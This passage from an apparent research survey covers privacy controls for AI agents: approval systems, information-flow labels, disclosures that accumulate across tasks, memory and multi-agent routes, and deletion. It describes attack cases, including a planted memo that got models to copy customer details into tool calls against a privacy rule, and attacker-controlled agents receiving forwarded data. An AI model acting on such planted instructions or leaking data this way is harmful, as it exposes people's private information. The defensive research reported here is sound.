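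| Agent | Tasks completed without any approval | Approvals needed across completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| Labels and checks added | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | About 17 |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals to FIDES's 36.8, but completed slightly fewer tasks when approvals were available (73.2% against 75.7%).

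Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a whole document instead of approving each action that follows from it, so for an email with ten tasks, one endorsement can replace ten approvals. Kolluri and colleagues decided against a similar option for declassifying private data, because whether a disclosure is appropriate depends heavily on the situation. But their policy for sending data, like the channel-posting rule, allows any message as long as the context is trusted. A user who confirms that an email is trustworthy therefore also lets the agent send confidential data to people who aren't allowed to read it.

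No people took part in these experiments. The counts assume that a person would approve every legitimate action and stop every attack. In the study by Hossain and colleagues, however, reviewers approved a quarter of unsafe requests even with the best design.

When APPA blocks a call, it lists the permitted ways forward. These may include completing a missing step, running an approved redaction tool, getting a ruling that covers only that call, or doing the reading in a temporary copy of the agent. Before a call runs, APPA also works out what label it would produce. This matters for a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it in one step, because a check of the agent's current label would find nothing wrong.

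Kravchenko and colleagues prove that once a message has become too restricted for its recipient, reading more data can never make it releasable, so the agent needs a ruling or an approved transformation. On 20 simulated corporate tasks, agents with APPA completed 88% to 90% of runs, depending on the model. With one of the models, completion fell to 35.0% when the software no longer suggested ways forward, and to 56.5% when the agent couldn't make temporary copies. On a second benchmark, completion ranged from 64.2% to 76.7%. No attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs across the two benchmarks.

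Completion rates don't measure how much work this leaves for people, because a fixed rule, a person or another model can make each ruling. If an operator assigns the rulings to people, they may face the same fatigue as before, a problem Kravchenko and colleagues leave to future work. Assigning the rulings to a model would reduce the number of requests people receive, but a model would again be judging which data may be released, within any limits the operator sets.

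## Disclosures that accumulate across tasks, memory and agents

The person, model or fixed rule that decides what an agent may share usually checks one message at a time. Even if every decision is correct, the recipient can still learn something from the messages together that nobody would have approved.

### Two averages and a salary

Suppose an agent may report average pay for any group of at least three people. On Monday a manager asks for the average of a five-person team and gets 60,000. On Tuesday she asks for the average of the same team without Ana and gets 55,000. She can now work out what Ana earns:

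```
Five people:    5 × 60,000 = 300,000
Without Ana:    4 × 55,000 = 220,000
Ana's salary:   300,000 − 220,000 = 80,000
```

Both groups are large enough, and neither answer contains anyone's salary. The manager may not have planned it. If an agent puts the team's average pay and headcount in a monthly report, readers can compare two reports to calculate the salary of anyone who left between them, provided nothing else changed.

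To block Tuesday's answer, a check would need a record of who received Monday's answer and which people it covered. It could then detect that the two groups differ by one person. This comparison doesn't require salary data, so the refusal reveals nothing about Ana's pay.

Comparing groups two at a time isn't enough, though. Suppose the manager gets these totals instead:

```
Ana + Ben + Carla         = 190,000
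Ana + Dev + Eli           = 190,000
Ben + Carla + Dev + Eli   = 220,000
```

No two of these groups differ by just one person, but adding the first two totals and subtracting the third leaves 160,000, which is twice Ana's salary. The check therefore has to test each new answer against all combinations of earlier ones. For totals and averages, software can do this with linear algebra. The check also has to treat people who might share their answers as one recipient, and it can't account for what they have learned elsewhere.

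### Clues from different conversations

Facts in ordinary text can combine in the same way, but no formula lists the combinations. *Can Agents Keep Secrets They Were Never Told?* (Yang, Yang et al., 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to note the date of an appointment. In a later session she mentions the code she used to book it, and in another the agent sees a public directory that lists the code as a counselling programme at a named clinic. None of these records looks sensitive when the agent stores it, but together they show that she is going to counselling, and where and when. The agent might mention this while writing a packing list.

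They tested six memory systems on 288 invented cases of this kind, with a small model, Qwen3.5-9B, writing the answers. The tasks didn't require the sensitive connection, and the model was instructed not to volunteer private facts. In 5.9% to 13.9% of cases, depending on the memory system, it still stated the whole connection in at least two of three attempts. The rate was 22.9% when the model could read all the earlier conversations and zero when it could read none. The model completed at most about a fifth of the tasks with any of the six systems, so a more capable agent might have a quite different rate.

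A separate test removed the clues that linked the sessions but left every sensitive value in place. Removing the clues could change whether the model stated the connection, so a scan of the memory for sensitive values would miss part of the risk.

### How mistakes build up with use

An agent that works for someone over many months also has more chances to make ordinary mistakes. For *CIMemories*, Mireshghallah, Mangaokar and colleagues (2025) invented 10 people with an average of 147 facts each, on topics such as health, money, housing and relationships. They gave a model all of one person's facts as memories and had it write messages for about 46 tasks, such as applying for a loan or negotiating a lease. On average, a task needed about 7 of the facts, while about 84 were inappropriate to share.

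GPT-5 labelled the facts by playing three people, as a model did in the tests by Guo and colleagues, and only unanimous labels counted. The violation rate is the share of facts that the model revealed in at least one task where it should have withheld them, over five runs of every task. Completeness is the share of necessary facts that it included:

| Model | Violations | Completeness |
|---|---|---|
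| GPT-4o | 14.82% | 43.95% |
| GPT-5 | 25.08% | 56.61% |
| o3 | 38.51% | 55.0% |
| Llama-3.3 70B | 44.43% | 53.99% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 44.44% | 59.07% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 46.35% | 52.83% |
| Mistral-7B | 56.94% | 46.56% |
| Qwen-3 32B | 69.14% | 57.63% |

With one run per task, GPT-5's violation rate rose from 0.1% after one task to 9.6% after 40. Running the same prompts five times raised it to 25.1%.

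Some growth is inevitable, because a fact that has leaked once stays on the list. If a fact has a probability *p* of leaking in each message, its chance of leaking at least once in *n* messages is:

```
1 − (1 − p)^n
```

With a 1% chance per message, that comes to 33% after 40 messages. The five repeated runs are more informative. If GPT-5 had revealed the same facts every time, the rate would have stayed at 9.6%, and if every fact had been equally likely to leak in each run, it would have reached about 40%. The actual figure lies between the two, so GPT-5 tended to leak certain facts but also leaked others more or less at random. (A user who generates five drafts and sends one discloses only what is in that one.)

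The violation rate also combines all the recipients. In the tests, one message told a landlord about a suspended nursing licence, and another told a university's financial aid office about a change in blood-pressure medicine. Those two recipients are unlikely to exchange what they were told. The 25.1% therefore measures how many of a person's facts have reached somebody who shouldn't have them. It doesn't measure what a single recipient could piece together, as the manager did with Ana's salary.

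Stricter privacy prompts reduced GPT-5's violations but also its completeness. When Mireshghallah and colleagues added inappropriate facts to its memory and kept the number of necessary ones constant, violations rose steadily and completeness didn't change. This is a good reason to keep memories small. The results may be hard to check because, according to *Mitigating Over-Personalization in LLMs via Structured Memory* (2026), much of the released dataset has empty labels.

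### Data that builds up in messages and tools

When several agents share a job, each can accumulate data too. In the AgentLeak tests by El Yagoubi and colleagues, there were far more leaks in messages between agents than in final answers. Shared memory held data it shouldn't have in 46.7% of multi-agent runs. In a smaller sample of 100 scenarios per model, agents put such data into tool inputs in 62% to 86% of cases.

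On a set of tasks without an attacker, a filter on final answers reduced their leak rate from 48% to 1% but left the internal leak rate at 31%. A prototype that also masked forbidden fields in messages and memory entries cut internal leakage from 31.5% to 2.4%. Task success fell from 78.6% to 73.9%, mostly because some agents needed the masked data.

The company that runs a tool can keep whatever an agent sends it in each call. In *The Claws in Plain Sight*, Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026) asked five DeepSeek and Claude models to draft a neutral product offer as a tool call. The models could see an invented customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, but were not supposed to pass on any of these details. The call had fields where the details would fit, and in most sessions a memo claimed that a compliance review required them.

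The models copied at least one of the four details into the call in 60 of 120 sessions. In those 60, they copied 3.25 details on average. The prompt contained a privacy rule in 90 of the sessions, and the models broke it in 40. With the strictest rule, which explicitly overrode such memos, the two DeepSeek models copied none of the details, but the three Claude models still copied some in 8 of 18 sessions. The experiment captured the calls without sending them and used the same task in every session, so it shows that the failure happens but not how common it is.

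A monitor that reads only an agent's explanations could miss these disclosures. In their 26 leaking sessions, the DeepSeek models never described what they were doing as an exception to the rule. Dong and colleagues propose software that checks every value in a call against its source, purpose and destination before the call runs. It can also recognise values derived in ways the developer has registered, such as a "premium" tier worked out from someone's income. In a small test on prepared calls, it blocked all 21 forbidden calls and allowed all 3 permitted ones. Those calls included complete records of where each value came from, which a real agent may not have.

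### Judging the whole route

A check on each transfer can also fail because the next recipient is acceptable but a later one isn't. A scheduling agent may need to know about a medical appointment, for example, but might then pass the details to a notification agent that an attacker controls. Wu, Delattre and Cao (2026), in *Judging Before Propagation*, therefore judge the planned route before the data leaves memory. Their method represents the job as a graph that records each agent's assigned task and the transfers planned between agents. When an agent asks for something from memory:

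1. The software splits the result into single facts, each with a subject, a type and a value.
2. For each fact, a judge model considers the transfers along the planned route. It takes into account the five parameters of contextual integrity, the recipient's task and what that recipient has already received.
3. The software releases the fact along an approved part of the route or blocks it.
4. It adds each approved fact to the recipients' histories before judging the next one, so that two facts in the same result can't slip through together.

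The method has two modes. "Full-scope" mode blocks a fact if any recipient along its route is unsuitable. "Auto-region" mode shares the fact as far along the route as is allowed, and a filter removes it from any message that would take it further. An unsuitable agent late in the workflow then doesn't keep earlier agents from getting information they need.

The researchers tested both modes on 144 invented cases in healthcare, finance, human resources and everyday life. Each case had four agents, one or two of them under an attacker's control, and 30 facts in memory, of which the job needed seven. These are the results with Claude Haiku 4.5 as the agents and GPT-5.6 Luna as the judge:

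| Check | Unauthorised disclosures per case | Questions answered correctly |
|---|---|---|
| None | 15.84 | 80.97% |
| Release from memory only, with recipient's history | 10.47 | 83.26% |
| Each transfer separately, as it happens | 6.11 | 80.69% |
| Planned route, auto-region | 1.49 | 80.00% |
| Planned route, full-scope | 0.62 | 77.92% |

Checking the route clearly worked better than checking single transfers. It reduced correct answers only slightly, though the size of the reduction depended on the judge. When Haiku did both jobs, correct answers fell from 81.04% without protection to 62.22% in full-scope mode. The judge also processed more than 130,000 tokens per case in either mode.

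Without protection, the largest group of disclosures involved facts that agents had passed on too far, and the method also improved most over the simpler checks on these disclosures. The results are therefore stronger evidence for checking in advance where information will go than for detecting dangerous combinations. The method also assumes that the workflow stays the same throughout, but many agents change their plans partway through.

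The histories include facts that the software has approved but not yet delivered, so they can overstate what a recipient knows. Wu and colleagues also assume that a disclosure acceptable to someone who knows a lot is acceptable to someone who knows less. That holds for Ana's salary, where knowing the first average makes the second one dangerous. But telling a colleague a diagnosis is harmless if they already know it and harmful if they don't. If the history wrongly lists the diagnosis as known, the judge could approve revealing it.

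### Simulating what a recipient could infer

*PrivacyFlow* (Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues, 2026) has an agent work out the consequences of its plan before it acts. The agent lists the data it intends to send, where that data came from and what each recipient probably knows already. A second step simulates what each recipient could infer from the combination. In one trial, a meeting agenda that mentioned "remediation actions" would have revealed a confidential audit to the manager under investigation. Further steps compare the plan with the norms of the context, then approve it, block it or ask the user. If the plan discloses too much, the agent first tries leaving information out, then making it less specific.

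They tested it on 986 sequences averaging six tasks, in which new emails, notes and calendar entries arrived between tasks. Each sensitive fact had a hidden list of people who were allowed to know it. A sequence passed only if the agent disclosed nothing to anyone else in any of its tasks:

| Model | Sequences without a violation: before / after | Average task score: before / after |
|---|---|---|
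| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 52.9% / 75.1% | 0.970 / 0.942 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 51.6% / 81.7% | 0.846 / 0.759 |
| GPT-5.4 | 38.3% / 75.3% | 0.922 / 0.766 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 37.8% / 68.8% | 0.964 / 0.909 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 14.6% / 69.8% | 0.902 / 0.716 |
| Kimi K2 | 13.0% / 58.8% | 0.892 / 0.780 |

The unprotected agents look much safer when each task is judged separately. Gemini 3.8 Flash, for example, had no violation in 89.5% of tasks. If its violations were independent, it would get through six tasks without one about 51% of the time, close to the 52.9% observed. Its violation rate also stayed between 9.6% and 12.4% from the first task to the seventh. The low pass rates for whole sequences therefore seem to come mainly from having more chances to fail, and there is little sign that this agent became more likely to fail as its context grew.

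Instructing the agent to protect privacy worked less well than PrivacyFlow. The instruction lowered Gemini 3.8 Flash's pass rate for sequences to 46.5% and raised Kimi K2's only to 16.5%. But with Gemini 3.8 Flash, PrivacyFlow took almost four times as long as the unprotected agent. No software enforces the approved plan either, so the model that carries it out can still send something else. Staab and colleagues examined 200 remaining failures and traced 90% to the first two steps, where the agent rates how sensitive the data is and plans what to send. The simulation can't do much to protect data that the agent has already misjudged as harmless.

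### Controls over time

Most other controls depend on a disclosure history, because an operator can't limit or withdraw disclosures that nobody has recorded. GAAP keeps such a history for a single user. The history has to outlast the agent's memory of the data, because without a record of Monday's average, a check would allow Tuesday's. A complete list of who knows which secrets would attract attackers, but a history can often hold less than the data itself. For the averages, it needs only the names of the people in each group.

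Cumulative limits cap what a recipient can learn in total. Counting requests is a poor way to do this, because two were enough to reveal Ana's salary. Differential privacy offers a better measure for statistics. The software adds random noise to each answer, deducts the answer's privacy loss, ε, from a total budget, and stops answering when the budget runs out. The noise makes this method of little use for small teams. If salaries can be anything from 0 to 200,000, the standard method with an ε of 1 changes the mean salary of five people by 40,000 on average, but that of 5,000 people by only 40. Wu and colleagues cite a system called OCELOT that applies a privacy budget to an agent's whole run. Applying a budget to free text, however, still requires an estimate of how much each sentence reveals.

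Expiry removes a stored fact or ends a permission on a set date. The note that Tom Reed is covering for Priya isn't needed after 30 June, and if it expires then, the agent can't mention her absence in August. Expiry in the agent's memory doesn't affect an outside service that keeps receiving new data. In *PriMobiBench* (2026), a model that read a phone agent's screenshots could reconstruct between 66.5% and 76.3% of a 25-item user profile after each of four tasks, even though some of the items changed between tasks.

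#### Does deletion work?

Deleting a memory should stop the agent from repeating it, but commercial products don't do this reliably. Jarin, Le and Markopoulou (2026), in *ForgetMeNot*, told five assistants facts about invented users in ordinary conversation and later asked about each fact directly. The table gives the leakage rates for four of them:

| Assistant | Saved memory on | After deleting everything |
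|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | 35.0% | 26.7% |
| Copilot | 24.8% | 23.8% |
| Gemini | 10.3% | 0.0% |
| Claude | 10.1% | 0.6% |

The fifth assistant, Replika, still had a rate of 13.4% after deletion. The study used only two invented users, and the results varied between sets of accounts. In a second set, where the conversations included pasted text with cues such as "remember", Copilot's rate after deletion was only 1.9%, while Gemini's was 7.9%.

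The memory pages also don't list everything the assistants have stored, so users can't choose to delete the unlisted facts. Direct questions showed that the assistants had stored a larger share of the tested facts than the pages listed, by an average of 21 percentage points. Stored facts can reach other people as well. In a trial where Gemini had email access, it disclosed 59 of 83 facts to an outside recipient at least once, although the conversations where it did so hadn't mentioned them.

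Even when deletion works reliably, it has to cover everything the agent made from the original. A memory system may have merged the appointment date and the booking code into one note, and another agent may hold a summary of that note. An operator can find this derived material only if the software recorded its sources, which information-flow labels could help it do.

#### After the recipient has the data

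Revocation withdraws a permission before it expires. Priya may change her mind about telling the consultant about her treatment, so the agent must check her current decision before its next message instead of relying on an approval it saved last week. Revocation can't take back the message the agent sent yesterday, and as Yang and colleagues point out, deleting the agent's records doesn't erase what a recipient has learned.

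| Control | What it can still do once a recipient has the data |
|---|---|
| Disclosure history | Identify who has it, so that the agent withholds facts that would add to it and the operator knows whom to ask to delete it |
| Cumulative limit | Block further answers |
| Expiry | End future access, but not remove a copy |
| Deletion from memory | Stop the agent from repeating it to others |
| Revocation | Stop further sharing and prompt a request for deletion |

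The operator can delete data from its own agents' memories, shared files and logs. To get outsiders to delete it, the operator has to rely on their cooperation, a contract or a legal right to deletion, and it may be unable to check whether they complied. Sending a link instead of a copy helps a little, because the operator can disable the link, but the recipient may already have read or saved the contents. The owner of a password or card number can replace it and make the old one useless, but Ana can't do that with her salary.
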